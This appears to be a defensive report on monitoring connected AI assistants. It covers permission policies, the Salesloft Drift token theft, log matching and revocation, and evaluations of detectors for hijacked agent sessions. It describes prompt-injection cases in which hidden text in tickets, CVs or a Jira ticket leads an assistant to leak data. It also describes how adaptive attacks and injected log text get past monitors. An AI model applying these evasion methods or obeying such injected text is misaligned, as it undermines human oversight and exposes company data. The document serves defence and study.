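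Connectors can often do more than their names suggest. According to PromptArmor, a mail connector can forward, delete and schedule messages, and a calendar connector can cancel events and change shared calendars. Users may also grant every permission an application requests. Context.ai's *Security Update* (2026) reports that an employee of Vercel, a web hosting company, connected Context.ai's AI office tool to a work account and chose "Allow All".

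The Australian Signals Directorate and its Five Eyes partners recommend credentials that expire when a job is complete. That would give a thief less time to use a stolen credential, but a hijacked assistant can send an email within seconds, before the credential expires.

### Four kinds of event

Denied calls are the easiest events to find because some component has already refused them. Solace's *Managing Audit and Compliance*, the documentation for an agent platform, suggests an alert on the rate of denied calls for each tool. A sudden rise may be an early sign of an attack, or it may have happened because an administrator recently removed a scope.

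A permitted call can fall outside the assistant's stated purpose, as when a recruiting assistant opens a budget. Detecting this requires a statement of the purpose and a log of which file the assistant opened. An assistant can also make an unusually large number of permitted calls, which software can detect by counting them.

The hardest event to find is a permitted flow in which the assistant reads from one connector and sends through another. In PromptArmor's example, an assistant can read a company's internal Confluence pages and reply to customers' support tickets in Zendesk. A customer who hides instructions in a ticket might receive an internal page in the reply. The assistant routinely reads pages and answers tickets, so neither call is suspicious on its own.

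Log settings can exclude permitted calls. Solace's platform logs a refused tool call as a warning, with the scopes the call required, and a successful one as ordinary information. A company that stored only warnings would have no record of the successful calls. The platform also leaves tool arguments out of its audit log to protect private content, so the log could show an unusual number of calls, but not which page the assistant read or what it told the customer.

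### A policy for a recruiting helper

Suppose a company has an assistant that arranges interviews and passes applications to the interviewers. The table sets out an invented policy for it.

| Connector | What the token permits | What the policy allows | Daily limit |
|---|---|---|---|
| Mail | Reading and sending all mail in the recruiting inbox | Reading applications, and writing to candidates and interviewers | 80 messages sent |
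| Calendar | Reading and changing every event on the recruiters' calendars | Finding free times, and creating or moving interviews | 40 events changed |
| Files | Reading every file the recruiters can open | Reading CVs, job descriptions and interview notes in the hiring folder | 200 files opened |

Under another rule, CVs and interview notes may go to interviewers but not outside the company. Here is how the policy would apply to six calls.

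| Call | Does the token permit it? | Kind of event | Response |
|---|---|---|---|
| Opens a CV in the hiring folder | Yes | None | None |
| Tries to create a public link to a CV | No | Denied call | Record it, and review repeated attempts |
| Opens the company's salary bands | Yes | Outside the stated purpose | Alert |
| Opens its 201st CV of the day | Yes | Unusual volume | Pause and ask the recruiter |
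| Emails a CV to tomorrow's interviewer | Yes | Flow from files to mail | Allow |
| Sends a candidate an invitation with interview notes attached | Yes | Flow from files to calendar | Hold for approval |

The token alone would stop only the public link. The 201st CV may be harmless, for example if a recruiter is searching old applications to fill a new vacancy. The email and the calendar invitation both carry hiring documents from one connector to another, so software has to check the recipients of both against a current list of interviewers. A company that monitors only outgoing mail would miss the invitation.

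A single connector can be enough to leak data. The recruiting inbox contains messages from strangers and private messages from colleagues, and the assistant can send mail from it. PromptArmor, following Willison, treats this combination of untrusted text, sensitive data and a way to send data out as the main danger. The flow rule should therefore also apply when the assistant reads and sends through the same mailbox.

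An assistant can cause harm even while following a good policy. For example, hidden text in a CV could lead it to recommend the candidate to every interviewer, when the policy allows it to read CVs and write to interviewers.

### The theft of Salesloft Drift tokens

In August 2025, outsiders copied companies' customer records using access those companies had granted to Drift, an AI chatbot from the sales software company Salesloft. Companies put Drift on their websites to talk to visitors and turn the conversations into sales leads in Salesforce, so Drift held tokens for their Salesforce accounts.

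According to Clari/Salesloft's *Trust Center*, the attacker had access to Salesloft's account on GitHub, which hosts program code, between March and June. The attacker then got into Drift's Amazon cloud environment and took customers' tokens, without having to trick the chatbot. Arcade, a vendor of software for agents, calls an application that stores many such tokens a "high-value token vault", because one break-in exposes every connected customer.

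Google's advisory on the incident, *Widespread Data Theft Targets Salesforce Instances via Salesloft Drift* (Larsen, Lin and colleagues, 2025), dates the Salesforce thefts from 8 August to at least 18 August. The attacker exported large amounts of data and searched it for passwords and keys to other systems. Google told The Hacker News (2025) that it knew of more than 700 organisations that might be affected.

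Cloudflare (2025), an internet infrastructure company, was one of the victims and published a detailed timeline from its logs. The last column below classifies the timeline's entries by the kinds of event described above, on the assumption that a chatbot for website visitors had no need to survey Cloudflare's Salesforce records.

| August 2025 (UTC) | Activity in Cloudflare's Salesforce account | Kind of event |
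|---|---|---|
| 12th, 22:14 | Logs in with the integration's credential and lists the types of record | Outside the stated purpose |
| 13th, 19:33 | Reads the structure of support cases and retrieves case data with a broad query | Outside the stated purpose, and perhaps unusual volume |
| 14th, 00:17 | Counts accounts, contacts and users | Outside the stated purpose |
| 14th, 11:09 | Checks whether this is the live system and reads its usage limits | Outside the stated purpose |
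| 16th, 19:28 | Counts the support cases | Outside the stated purpose |
| 17th, 11:11 | Exports the text of the cases in just over three minutes | Unusual volume |
| 17th, 11:15 | Deletes the export job | Outside the stated purpose |

A volume alert on the final export would probably have come too late, because the export took only minutes. An alert for activity outside the chatbot's purpose could have caught the thief at any point in the roughly four and a half days before that. A volume alert might also have caught the broad query on 13 August, which took customer data and produced one of the larger early responses. Cloudflare learned of the problem on 23 August, when Salesforce and Salesloft contacted it. Deleting the job removed the main evidence of the export, but Cloudflare reconstructed the theft from other logs.

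### Matching the two logs

Salesforce recorded these calls under Drift's credential, although Drift had not made them. A company can look for such calls by comparing the connected service's log with the assistant's. For each call the service logged under the assistant's credential, software searches the assistant's log for an entry with the same account, operation and item at about the same time. A call with no matching entry suggests that the token was stolen.

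The check needs both logs, and the customer may have only one. Customers of Drift, a chatbot run by Salesloft, could look in Salesforce's log but not necessarily in Salesloft's. Cloudflare considers logs of traffic between two outside companies essential but acknowledges that they can be difficult to capture. Sometimes the check needs a third log. Hyperagent's *Composio Security Incident* (2026) explains that Hyperagent, an agent product, connected to outside services through another company, Composio. An investigator might have to follow a call from Hyperagent through Composio to GitHub.

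The logs also need enough detail. Suppose software compares only the account and the time, and accepts any assistant entry within w minutes before or after the service's entry. If the assistant makes λ calls a minute at random times, the probability that a thief's call will match one of them by chance is:

$$P = 1 - e^{-2\lambda w}$$

With 30 calls an hour and a window of one minute either way, the chance of a false match is 63%. Comparing the file or record as well would remove most false matches, but this isn't possible with a log like Solace's, which omits arguments. A better method is for the assistant's software to attach a new random identifier to every request. A thief could invent an identifier, but it wouldn't appear in the assistant's log. This works only if the connected service records the identifiers.

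Many unmatched calls are harmless. One search by an assistant may cause dozens of calls to a file store, and some connectors copy new files when nobody is using the assistant. Missing entries in the assistant's log also make legitimate calls look like theft. The company has to learn these patterns before it can treat an unmatched call as an emergency.

Salesloft gave its customers a simpler check that needs no log from Drift. Genuine Drift traffic comes only from a published list of network addresses, so a successful connection from any other address is suspect. Both addresses in Cloudflare's timeline are on Salesloft's separate list of malicious addresses, so the check would have flagged the first login on 12 August if Cloudflare had been using it. Cloudflare now recommends restricting such connections by address, which would block the calls as well as reveal them.

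An attacker inside the vendor's systems may defeat both checks. In May 2026, an attacker broke into Composio and eventually could run code in the environment where Composio executes tool calls, according to Composio (2026). Calls made from that environment could come from Composio's usual addresses, and the attacker might also be able to create matching log entries.

Matching also stops helping once a thief has used the token to get other credentials. In the Context.ai incident, the attacker took over the employee's Google account and used it to enter the employee's Vercel account (Vercel, 2026). From there, the attacker reached an internal system and read customers' stored settings. A comparison with Context.ai's log could have exposed only the calls made with its token.

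The check also doesn't detect prompt injection, because a hijacked assistant makes the calls itself and each one therefore has a match. Detecting prompt injection still requires the alerts for purpose, volume and flow.

### Who writes the policy, and how it goes stale

The recruiting manager knows which folders the assistant needs, and the security team knows what an attacker could do with them, so they should probably write the policy together. The company also needs to name someone who can decide whether an unusual call was legitimate. Otherwise, whoever receives the alert may be unable to resolve it.

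Without a written policy, the vendor's defaults and employees' choices determine what the assistant can do. PromptArmor found that ChatGPT's connected apps are on by default for Business customers but off for Enterprise and Edu customers. Vercel was not a Context.ai customer, but one of its employees chose "Allow All", and Vercel's Google settings appear to have permitted it, according to Context.ai.

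Administrators can enforce part of a policy through the vendor's settings. Claude lets them allow a connector's tool, block it or require approval for each use. ChatGPT lets them choose individual actions for an app and decide in advance whether to enable all new actions, only those that read data, or none. If they enable all new actions, an update can let the assistant do something that nobody at the company has reviewed.

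A policy can also become outdated without an update. Someone may start saving job offers, with salaries, in the hiring folder. An interviewer may leave the company but remain on the list of approved recipients. Recruiters may begin using the assistant to check references, so legitimate emails to former employers trigger alerts every day. Staff may then ignore the alerts or loosen the rule until it allows almost any recipient.

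An expiry date on each permission would force a periodic review. Reviewers can use the log to find scopes the assistant hasn't used for months and forbidden calls that turned out to be legitimate. Removing an unused scope is usually safe, although a job that runs only once a year may still need it.

### Restricting permissions automatically

The Five Eyes agencies advise developers to set up "trigger-action protocols" that automatically restrict an agent's permissions when it behaves unexpectedly. The agencies leave companies to decide what counts as unexpected, which permissions to remove and when to restore them. By Cloudflare's timeline, an analyst would have had about three minutes to notice the export and stop it, so the response may have to be automatic.

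Under this rule, false alarms waste many hours of work. The detector in the base-rate example raises about 50 false alarms a day and a real alert on two days out of three, or about 75 false alarms for every real one. If each false alarm restricts an assistant and delays its user by half an hour, the company loses 25 hours of work a day. The rule is therefore worthwhile only if a correct restriction prevents, on average, more harm than the loss of about 37 hours of work (75 times half an hour).

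A leak of customer records could easily cost more than that. But many alerts concern smaller incidents, and the calculation leaves out how people respond. Employees who keep losing access may move to an assistant that the company doesn't monitor.

Composio's response to its breach shows how automatic restrictions can affect legitimate users. It limited existing API keys, the credentials its customers' software uses, to network addresses that each customer had used in the previous two weeks. This could block a customer with a valid key who connected through a VPN or whose address had changed. Composio also revoked 5,241 keys that the attacker might have seen, and warned that this might have caused customer downtime. The measures may have been worth the disruption because the attack was real, but a false alarm would have caused the same disruption for no benefit.

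A company can reduce the disruption by removing only the permissions that make the suspected attack dangerous. If the recruiting assistant opens the salary bands, the software could suspend sending and sharing but let the assistant keep reading CVs and drafting messages. The recruiter would send the drafts by hand until someone had reviewed the alert. Milder restrictions also limit the disruption an applicant can cause by deliberately triggering the rule with hidden text in a CV.

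The software has to apply the restriction at the point the attacker is using. Turning off a tool in the assistant can stop a hijacked assistant, but it has no effect on a thief who uses a stolen token to call the mail service directly. If the logs suggest that a token was stolen, the company has to revoke it.

### Revoking a token

Revoking a token means telling the service that issued it to stop accepting it. The company should revoke the refresh token as well as the access token, because a thief could use the refresh token to get a new access token. Changing the user's password may not invalidate either token. Deleting the connection in the assistant's settings may not be enough either. Composio warned its customers that a deleted connection can leave behind a working token.

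The platform that holds a token can't always revoke it. Composio put the share of connections it couldn't revoke at under 5%. For example, Google refused Composio's revocation requests for some applications that a company's administrator had approved, so the administrator had to remove the application in Google's console. Many services also use API keys, which the customer usually has to replace at the service.

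Revocation has to cover every service the stolen tokens could access. On 20 August 2025, Salesloft and Salesforce revoked Drift's Salesforce tokens. *The Ongoing Fallout from a Breach at AI Chatbot Maker Salesloft* (Krebs on Security, 2025) points out that Salesloft's notice that day didn't mention stolen tokens. Salesloft also told customers who hadn't connected Drift to Salesforce that they weren't affected. But the attacker had also taken tokens for other services, including Slack, Microsoft Azure and OpenAI, and had used some on 9 August to read email in a few Google Workspace accounts. Google confirmed the email access on 28 August and advised customers to treat every token connected to Drift as potentially compromised.

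The stolen data may contain more credentials. Cloudflare found 104 of its API tokens in the support cases the attacker had copied and replaced them all, although it saw no sign of misuse. It also began replacing the secrets for its third-party integrations every week. Frequent replacement helps less if the attacker is still inside the vendor's systems and can copy the new secrets.

Staff can use the connected service's log to check whether a revocation worked. Any later attempt to use the old token should be logged as refused, and a successful call means whoever stole the token still has a working credential.

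## How well detectors judge whole sessions

In Maya's session, the assistant read a file, searched for another, failed to share it and sent an email. Assistants at her company probably do all of these things every day, so an alert for any one of them would mostly flag harmless sessions. The leak is visible only when someone looks at the steps together.

Rules can describe some of these combinations. *Efficient Auditing of Adversarial AI Agent Behavior from Agent Traces* (Zhang, Yang and Xu, 2026) uses "sequence rules", which fire when an action and an earlier entry in the same trace both match set conditions. For example, a rule can fire when sensitive data enters a session and the agent later tries to send something out. Other detectors learn the usual order of tool calls, convert each session into numbers for a classifier to score, or give the log to a language model to read.

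Some detectors only label the session, while others point to the suspicious step. The survey *Log Analysis for LLM-Based Agents* (2026) sorts research by this distinction. Pointing to the step saves investigators time, since a session can contain dozens of calls.

### Learning the usual order of calls

TraceAegis, the detector that Liu and colleagues designed to work from gateway logs, learns from past sessions the order in which an agent calls its tools. It arranges the tools in levels and accepts any order among tools on the same level. For example, the hospital agent always extracts a patient's symptoms before it consults a department, but it may consult orthopaedics and psychiatry in either order. A language model then summarises which inputs normally go with each sequence, such as knee or arm pain with a referral to orthopaedics. TraceAegis flags a new session if the order of calls is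 unfamiliar or the inputs don't fit the sequence.

Liu and colleagues tested it on the hospital agent and on one that files purchase requests for a car manufacturer. For each agent they generated 1,300 harmless traces and 300 abnormal ones. Half of the abnormal traces contained a new and malicious sequence of calls, and the other half kept a familiar sequence but altered its details. The results use a score called F1, which is high only if precision and recall are both high:

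$$F_1 = \frac{2 \times \text{precision} \times \text{recall}}{\text{precision} + \text{recall}}$$

Liu and colleagues report that TraceAegis achieved an F1 of 0.93 for the healthcare agent and 0.96 for the procurement agent. Their detailed results with the language model DeepSeek-V3 show nearly the same scores reversed, 0.965 for healthcare and 0.932 for procurement, so one of the two passages probably has the labels swapped. Without TraceAegis, DeepSeek-V3 scored about 0.85 on each agent. TraceAegis's performance also depends on the model, and with the smaller Gemma 3 it scored only 0.81 and 0.74.

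These scores depend on how common attacks were in the test. The published precision and recall imply that half of the test sessions were abnormal, and that TraceAegis with DeepSeek-V3 wrongly flagged about 10 of 300 harmless hospital sessions (3%) and 21 of 300 harmless procurement sessions (7%). If only one hospital session in 10,000 were compromised, precision would fall to about 0.003 and F1 to about 0.006.

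Liu and colleagues also tried TraceAegis at a technology company, on a system that looks for software vulnerabilities in five fixed stages. TraceAegis caught 132 of 140 attacks that disrupted the sequence. In one attack, a planted file led the system to write its report before running the check that the report was meant to describe. A filter that read each step separately would have had little to flag. Liu and colleagues give no false positive rate for this trial.

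All three systems follow a set routine, so the results probably don't carry over to an open-ended assistant. If Maya asks for something new to her company, the assistant may call its tools in an order absent from TraceAegis's training logs. TraceAegis would flag that session even if the assistant did exactly what she wanted. A company could train TraceAegis separately on a few repetitive tasks, such as processing invoices. The company would need to check the training logs carefully, because new sessions can add to the relations TraceAegis has learned but never remove one. TraceAegis would therefore treat an attack in those logs as normal until someone rebuilt the model.

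### Metadata and content

In *Content-Aware Attack Detection in LLM Agent Tool-Call Traffic*, Zavrak (2026) measured how much a detector can learn from different parts of the log. The main test used 80 tasks involving calendars, alarms, files, databases and web searches. Some detectors received only metadata: the tool's name, the length of its response and a short code computed from the arguments. Others received the content of the arguments and responses as embeddings, which are lists of numbers that are similar for texts with similar meanings.

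Zavrak compares the detectors by AUROC, the area under the receiver operating characteristic curve. It equals the probability that the detector gives a randomly chosen attacked session a higher score, s, than a randomly chosen harmless one:

$$\text{AUROC} = \Pr(s_{\text{attacked}} > s_{\text{harmless}})$$

Guessing gives 0.5, and a detector that scores every attacked session above every harmless one gets 1.

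Detectors that used only metadata scored 0.64. With content, neural networks scored between 0.89 and 0.92, and XGBoost, a much simpler method that combines many decision trees, scored 0.975. Most of the attacks changed a tool's arguments or results but not the choice of tool, so the metadata contained little evidence of them. This is a practical reason not to omit arguments and results from logs by default.

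The metadata detector would have scored much higher under a common way of testing. Researchers usually split sessions at random into training and test sets, so sessions from the same tasks appear in both. A detector can then learn which tools each task uses and recognise the tasks instead of the attacks. The metadata detector scored 0.898 with a random split, but 0.640 when Zavrak kept all sessions from a task on the same side of the split. A content detector fell less, from 0.992 to 0.891.

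Another weakness in the data is harder to fix. All 3,797 attacked sessions came from one language model, glm-4-flash, while the 605 harmless sessions came from eight, so a detector could score well by recognising how glm-4-flash writes. Zavrak acknowledges this and tested whether a classifier could identify the model from metadata. It scored 0.41, worse than guessing. But the detector's high scores depend on content, and Zavrak says it may have partly used the model's style. The data contained too few harmless glm-4-flash sessions to test the detector on that model alone.

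The results for different attacks suggest that style isn't the whole explanation. In one run, a neural network caught 87% of the attacks that altered both arguments and responses, but only 37% of those that altered arguments alone. Both kinds came from glm-4-flash, so a detector that had learned only to recognise the model should have caught them at similar rates. However, the 37% figure comes from just 57 sessions.

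Even if the 0.975 is sound, the detector would be hard to use by itself. At its default threshold, XGBoost caught 93% of attacked sessions and flagged about 7% of harmless ones, which would mean about 700 false alarms a day at a company with 10,000 daily sessions. On a second benchmark with shorter sessions and subtler attacks, the best AUROC was 0.78, even though Zavrak had trained the detectors on sessions from that benchmark.

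#### Why a high AUROC can mislead

AUROC does not change with the share of sessions that are compromised, so a detector can score well and still raise mostly false alerts when compromised sessions are rare. One detector that Abbasi and colleagues tested had an AUROC of 0.879. If 2% of sessions were compromised, which is probably far more than at most companies, it would raise about 12 false alerts for every real one. At 0.1%, only one alert in 250 would be real.

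A published precision is also hard to interpret without knowing how the researchers chose the harmless sessions. At the same 2%, the detector's precision was 11.7% when Abbasi and colleagues counted only ordinary harmless sessions and 3.9% when they counted only those that resembled attacks.

Abbasi and colleagues then trained detectors on AgentDrift, a set of simulated sessions, and tested them on AgentDojo. All scored between 0.47 and 0.52, which is no better than guessing. One of these methods reached 0.996 when trained on other AgentDojo tasks. The detectors had apparently learned how each dataset was made. For example, the text "2026" appeared in 74% of AgentDrift's harmless training sessions but in only 5% of the attacked ones.

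### Language models that read the log

A language model can judge sessions without training on attacks. AlignmentCheck, a monitor published by Meta, gives a model the user's request and the assistant's actions so far, and the model judges whether the latest action serves a goal the user didn't set. In Abbasi and colleagues' test, it scored 0.93 on AgentDojo, far above the detectors trained on AgentDrift. Meta had evaluated AlignmentCheck's prompt on AgentDojo, so the score may be somewhat inflated.

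AlignmentCheck still raised too many false alarms. With a Llama model, it flagged 90% of compromised AgentDojo sessions and 17% of harmless ones. With the newer Claude Sonnet 5.5, the false positive rate fell to 4% on AgentDojo but was 31% on AgentDrift, where more than a quarter of the harmless sessions resembled attacks. A company would have to measure the false positive rate on its own sessions before relying on the alerts.

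Training a model on security examples can make it worse at judging sessions. Del Rosario (2025), in *Temporal Attack Pattern Detection in Multi-Agent AI Workflows*, trained an eight-billion-parameter model on about 81,000 examples. Its score on multiple-choice security questions rose from 43% to 74%, but when it labelled 30 traces as benign, suspicious or malicious, it called 10 of the 15 benign ones malicious. This is the source of the 66.7% false positive rate cited in other papers.

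The figure is correct, but it comes from only 15 traces, which are compatible with a true rate anywhere from about 38% to 88%. It also makes the model look better than it was, because the model labelled the other five harmless traces suspicious. It called nine of the 15 attacks malicious and six suspicious. Staff who reviewed everything the model called suspicious or malicious would have reviewed all 30 traces.

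Del Rosario attributes this to the training data, about 90% of which concerned attacks. The model seems to have learned to treat any series of steps as dangerous. It mistook routine reporting for data theft when an agent queried a database, made a PDF and emailed it to a manager. Telling the model that most company workflows are harmless, and giving it an example of one, changed none of the totals.

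### Uber's two-stage detector

Having a capable model examine every session closely is slow and expensive, so Li and colleagues at Uber split the work between two models. GPT-4o reads every session and clears those that are plainly harmless. Claude Sonnet 4 investigates the rest, and can look up a tool's source code, descriptions of known attack techniques and the company's policies.

Li and colleagues tested their detector on 302 tasks that used 133 MCP servers. It caught 28 of 42 attacks and flagged none of the 260 harmless tasks. Three other detectors each caught 8 to 17 attacks and raised 30 to 40 false alarms. Li and colleagues also built the benchmark, so the comparison may favour their detector. On AgentDojo, which others built, the detector caught all 38 attacks and flagged three of 55 harmless tasks.

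Results varied widely by type of attack. The detector caught all nine attempts to bypass security controls or disrupt operations, but only one of the five that abused permissions. An assistant that misuses a legitimate permission, as Maya's did, may therefore be among the hardest to catch, though five cases are too few to be sure.

#### What no false alarms in 260 tasks can show

If a detector wrongly flags a share f of harmless tasks, the probability that it flags none of 260 is $(1-f)^{260}$. The highest rate that still leaves a 5% chance of such a result comes from:

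$$(1 - f)^{260} = 0.05 \quad\Rightarrow\quad f \approx 0.0115$$

The true rate of false alarms could therefore be as high as about 1.15%, or 115 a day at 10,000 sessions. With one compromised session a day and a recall of 67%, that would be about 170 false alarms for each real alert. Recall is uncertain too, since 28 of 42 is compatible with a true value between about 50% and 80%.

In the base-rate example, half the detector's alerts would be real only if it flagged no more than one harmless session in 15,000. Showing a rate that low would take about 45,000 harmless sessions without a false alarm. Uber handles that many sessions in five days, and staff would need to examine only the ones the detector flagged. Missed attacks are much harder to count because nobody knows which unflagged sessions were compromised, so a company has to plant test attacks to estimate how many the detector misses.

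#### What each part contributes

Li and colleagues removed parts of the system one at a time. When Claude investigated every task, recall rose from 67% to 80%, evidently because GPT-4o had been clearing some real attacks. The change also introduced two false alarms and raised the average time per task from 18.5 to 28.1 seconds.

Without access to the tools' source code, recall fell to 57%, and the published scores imply about five false alarms. Many of the attacks involved malicious tools, so a tool's code was more informative than its description. Removing the descriptions of known attacks lowered recall to 59%. Removing the company's policies made almost no difference, perhaps because most of the attacks broke obvious security rules.

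The full system cost 2.4 cents a task. If real sessions cost the same, 10,000 a day would come to $240. The cheapest of the other detectors cost a tenth of a cent per task, but it raised 34 false alarms, and the staff time spent on those would probably cost more than the detector saved.

#### Alerts in production

Uber's analysts labelled 34% of the alerts they reviewed as real, 17% as real but not malicious, and 49% as false. But the system had raised no false alarms on the benchmark. Li and colleagues explain that it had passed many of the falsely flagged sessions to a person as a precaution. GPT-4 wrote some of the benchmark's harmless tasks, which may have been easier to judge.

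A precision of 34% is still far higher than the 1.3% in the base-rate example, probably because most of the real alerts concerned exposed passwords and keys, which are common at Uber. Other kinds of attack were extremely rare, so we can infer very little from the 34% about how well the system finds hijacked assistants. Li and colleagues don't give the number of alerts per day, so we can't calculate a false positive rate.

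The prompt injection they describe from the deployment was a test. It re-created an attack in which an email generated a Jira ticket with hidden instructions, and a coding assistant that read the ticket sent out login credentials. The system flagged the injection, the credential access and the outgoing data.

### When the verdict arrives

Even a correct alert may come too late to stop an attack, because Zavrak's detector needs the complete session and Uber's sensor collects sessions once an hour. Such alerts still come soon enough for an investigation. *AgentTracer* (2026), for example, describes a system that starts from one suspicious tool call and works backwards through the log to the injected text. Its tests mixed the attack logs with 9,000 harmless calls from 1,800 user requests.

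Uber's alerts about exposed passwords came too late to prevent the leaks, and there were too many for staff to review. So Uber added a hook that checks each prompt before a coding assistant sends it. The hook can block a prompt if it contains text that is unusually random or has the format of a known type of credential.

The hook flagged 212 different credentials over hundreds of thousands of sessions, and 206 of them were real, a precision of 97.2%. Such a simple check can do well because many credentials have a recognisable format and people paste them often. Li and colleagues say the same approach fails for attacks that depend on what a tool does or why the assistant used it. They don't say how many credentials the hook missed.

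Stopping a hijacked assistant requires judging an action before it runs. Uber's full investigation takes about 30 seconds, so running it before each of the 28 calls in a typical task would make the user wait about 14 minutes longer. Zhang and colleagues reduce the delay by using fixed rules to choose which actions a language model should check. They used Claude Sonnet 5.5 both to check actions and to revise the rules and checking instructions over five rounds, based on examples of missed attacks and false alarms.

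The test used 149 recorded runs of an agent doing office work, 81 of them unsafe. Some of the unsafe runs began with a malicious request and others with the agent's carelessness, so the results aren't specific to prompt injection.

| Actions the model checks | Unsafe runs caught | Safe runs flagged | Checks per run | Tokens per run |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| All | 81.5% | 11.8% | 8.15 | 47,800 |
| Those chosen by the original rules | 37.0% | 13.2% | 6.64 | 34,000 |
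| Those chosen by the revised rules | 72.8% | 5.9% | 2.33 | 14,600 |

The revised rules used 69% fewer tokens (the units of text a model processes) and halved the false alarms, but missed more attacks. The false alarm rate also varies between sets of runs. The same rules and instructions flagged 24% of a separate set of 33 safe runs.

Some misses came from gaps in the log. The recordings identified browser clicks by a number and omitted the text of the button or link, so the rules could not distinguish a dangerous click from a harmless one. Of the ten runs that only the full check caught, five involved an action that the rules had skipped, and two of those actions were clicks.

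The next table puts the main results on a common scale. The tests used different attacks and different harmless sessions, so the table isn't a ranking.

| Detector | When it judges | Attacks caught | False alarms per 10,000 harmless sessions |
|---|---|---|---|
| Liu and colleagues, hospital agent | After the session | 96% | About 330 |
| Zavrak, XGBoost | After the session | 93% | About 710 |
| Abbasi and colleagues, AlignmentCheck with Llama on AgentDojo | After the session | 90% | About 1,700 |
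| Del Rosario, counting only "malicious" | After the session | 60% | About 6,700 |
| Li and colleagues, their own benchmark | Hourly in production | 67% | Between 0 and 115 |
| Zhang and colleagues, revised rules | Before selected actions | 73% | About 590 |

### Attackers who adapt

Nearly all of these tests used attacks that were fixed in advance. A real attacker who knows about a detector can change the attack until it gets through. Of the eleven detector evaluations that Abbasi and colleagues reviewed, only one included attackers who did this.

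Text filters have had harder tests. In *The Attacker Moves Second*, Nasr, Carlini and colleagues (2025) attacked 12 published defences with automated search and human testers, adapting the attacks to each defence. Most of the defences were originally reported to stop almost all attacks, but the adapted attacks succeeded more than 90% of the time against most of the 12. Four of the defences were detectors that screen text. The attacks succeeded more than 90% of the time against three of these detectors and 71% of the time against the fourth.

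Combining several detectors didn't stop the attacks either. This weakens the case for requiring two signals before an alert, because the calculation behind it assumes the attacker isn't trying to avoid either signal. Nasr and colleagues still consider detectors useful against unsophisticated attacks.

Detectors that judge actions may be harder to evade than those that judge wording, because the attacker eventually needs the assistant to do something harmful. But they can still be beaten. Nasr and colleagues also tested a defence that compares an assistant's tool calls in two separate runs, and their attacks succeeded against it 76% of the time, or 95% when they used knowledge of how it worked. Some session detectors also rely on features that an attacker controls. When Abbasi and colleagues changed only the length of the hostile text, one detector's recall fell from 77% to 3%. They did not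 check whether the altered attacks would still have fooled the assistant.

The researchers' automated search used the text detectors' scores to improve the attack after each attempt. Many attackers lack that feedback, because an outsider who emails a company's assistant usually can't tell whether a log monitor raised an alert. But attackers can practise on their own copy of a public detector, and both AlignmentCheck's prompt and Uber's detection code are public.

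*Scaling Adaptive Prompt Injection Attacks with Agent Swarms* (2026) supports the main finding of Nasr and colleagues. In its experiments, models became less resistant as the attacking model became more capable, but success rates were not always high. In one experiment, an adaptive attacker limited to 25 queries succeeded in 6 of 80 scenarios, compared with 2 for an earlier attack. Testing is also uneven across products, and *Benchmarking Web Agent Defenses Against Adaptive Visual Prompt Injection* (2026) describes adaptive testing of defences for web-browsing agents as still limited in scope.

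Persistence also helps attackers. *Adaptive Evaluation of Out-of-Band Defenses Against Prompt Injection in LLM Agents* (Narisetty, Kore and colleagues, 2026) cites Anthropic's figures for Claude Opus 4.5 in coding tasks, where attackers succeeded 4.7% of the time with one attempt, 33.6% with ten and 63% with a hundred. But repeated failures give a monitor more chances to notice the attack.

Fixed checks outside the model have done better so far. *Evaluation of Prompt Injection Defenses in Large Language Models* (2026) tested nine configurations against an attacker that learned from its failures. Every defence that relied on the model to protect itself eventually broke. Ordinary code that checked each reply before the user received it let nothing through in 15,000 attacks. The secrets in the test were planted in advance, so they were easier to look for than whatever a company might consider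 confidential.

Narisetty and colleagues tested Progent, which applies fixed rules to each tool call. Progent reduced the success rate of ordinary attacks from 25.8% to 4.2%, and an attack adapted to it succeeded 2.6% of the time. They used one small model and a single handwritten attack, and they say a stronger attack might still work.

### Text aimed at the model that reads the log

A language model that reads a log also reads any hostile text in it. An attacker could use that text to claim that the session was an authorised test or to give a false explanation for a suspicious transfer. Google's Gemini has had a similar flaw, in which injected text reached the assistant through a log.

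Li and colleagues list attempts to influence their detector as a risk. To address it, they keep model and prompt versions fixed, control changes and repeat their benchmark tests before each update. These measures should catch an update that makes the detector worse, but they protect less against a new attack on the current version. GPT-4o is the obvious target, because it cleared about 41% of the benchmark tasks without passing them on. An attacker who wrote the tool could also try to influence Claude through the source code it looks up.

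One remedy, used by AlignmentCheck, is to show the model the user's request and the assistant's tool calls but not what the tools returned. Injected text in a web page then can't reach the model directly, though some could still get through if the assistant copied it into an email or a search.

Leaving out the results also helps because a detector that reads them may flag injected text even if the assistant ignored it. AlignmentCheck with Claude Sonnet 5.5 flagged 6% of the failed attacks in AgentDojo, compared with 31% for a text classifier trained on that benchmark. A company that also wants to know about failed attempts could look for them separately.

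The model can also be allowed to explain a fixed rule's alert or raise its priority, but not dismiss it. For example, if a rule flagged a session that sent a confidential file to an unknown address, the alert would remain even if text in the session fooled the model. This would also keep some false alarms that the model could have removed, so it is practical only for rules that rarely flag harmless sessions.

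## Privacy, retention and tampering with logs

Zavrak's tests showed that detectors work much better when they can read the arguments and results of tool calls. But this content is also the most sensitive data an assistant handles. A full log of Maya's session would hold her request, the supplier's proposal, her company's price file and the text of an email. The file store and the mailbox each have their own access controls, but anyone who can read the log can read everything in it.

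Employees also tell assistants things they wouldn't put in a shared company system. Someone might ask for help with a resignation letter, a complaint about a manager or a medical diagnosis. The log may contain messages from customers and job applicants, who may not know the company uses an assistant. OpenTelemetry warns that its fields for message content, which are off by default, are likely to contain personal data.

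### Reducing what a log exposes

Software can redact sensitive text before it stores an entry. This works better for passwords and keys than for a sentence about someone's health. Redaction can also destroy evidence. If software deleted every email address from Maya's log, an investigator couldn't tell that the assistant had written to an outsider. Replacing each address with a consistent label, such as "outside-address-17", would preserve that fact and let the investigator find other sessions with the same address. The company would still need a list of which label stands for which address so that it could block the attacker's address.

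A second method is to store hashes instead of text, as Sharif requires. An investigator can then recognise only exact copies, because changing one character changes the hash. Sharif's format also hashes all the arguments of a tool call together, so an investigator checking whether Maya's email went to a suspected address would need the exact text of the email and every other argument.

Hashes protect short values poorly. A computer can hash all one million six-digit codes in about a second and see which one matches the hash in the log. The same method works for names on a staff list. Sharif therefore tells companies to look for personal data even in hashed form. A keyed hash also depends on a secret key, so people without the key can't guess values this way.

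The company can also keep the content in a separate store with stricter access rules. Detection software could read all of it, while a person would open only the sessions under investigation and record why. This keeps all the evidence, but an investigator may have to wait for approval while an attack continues.

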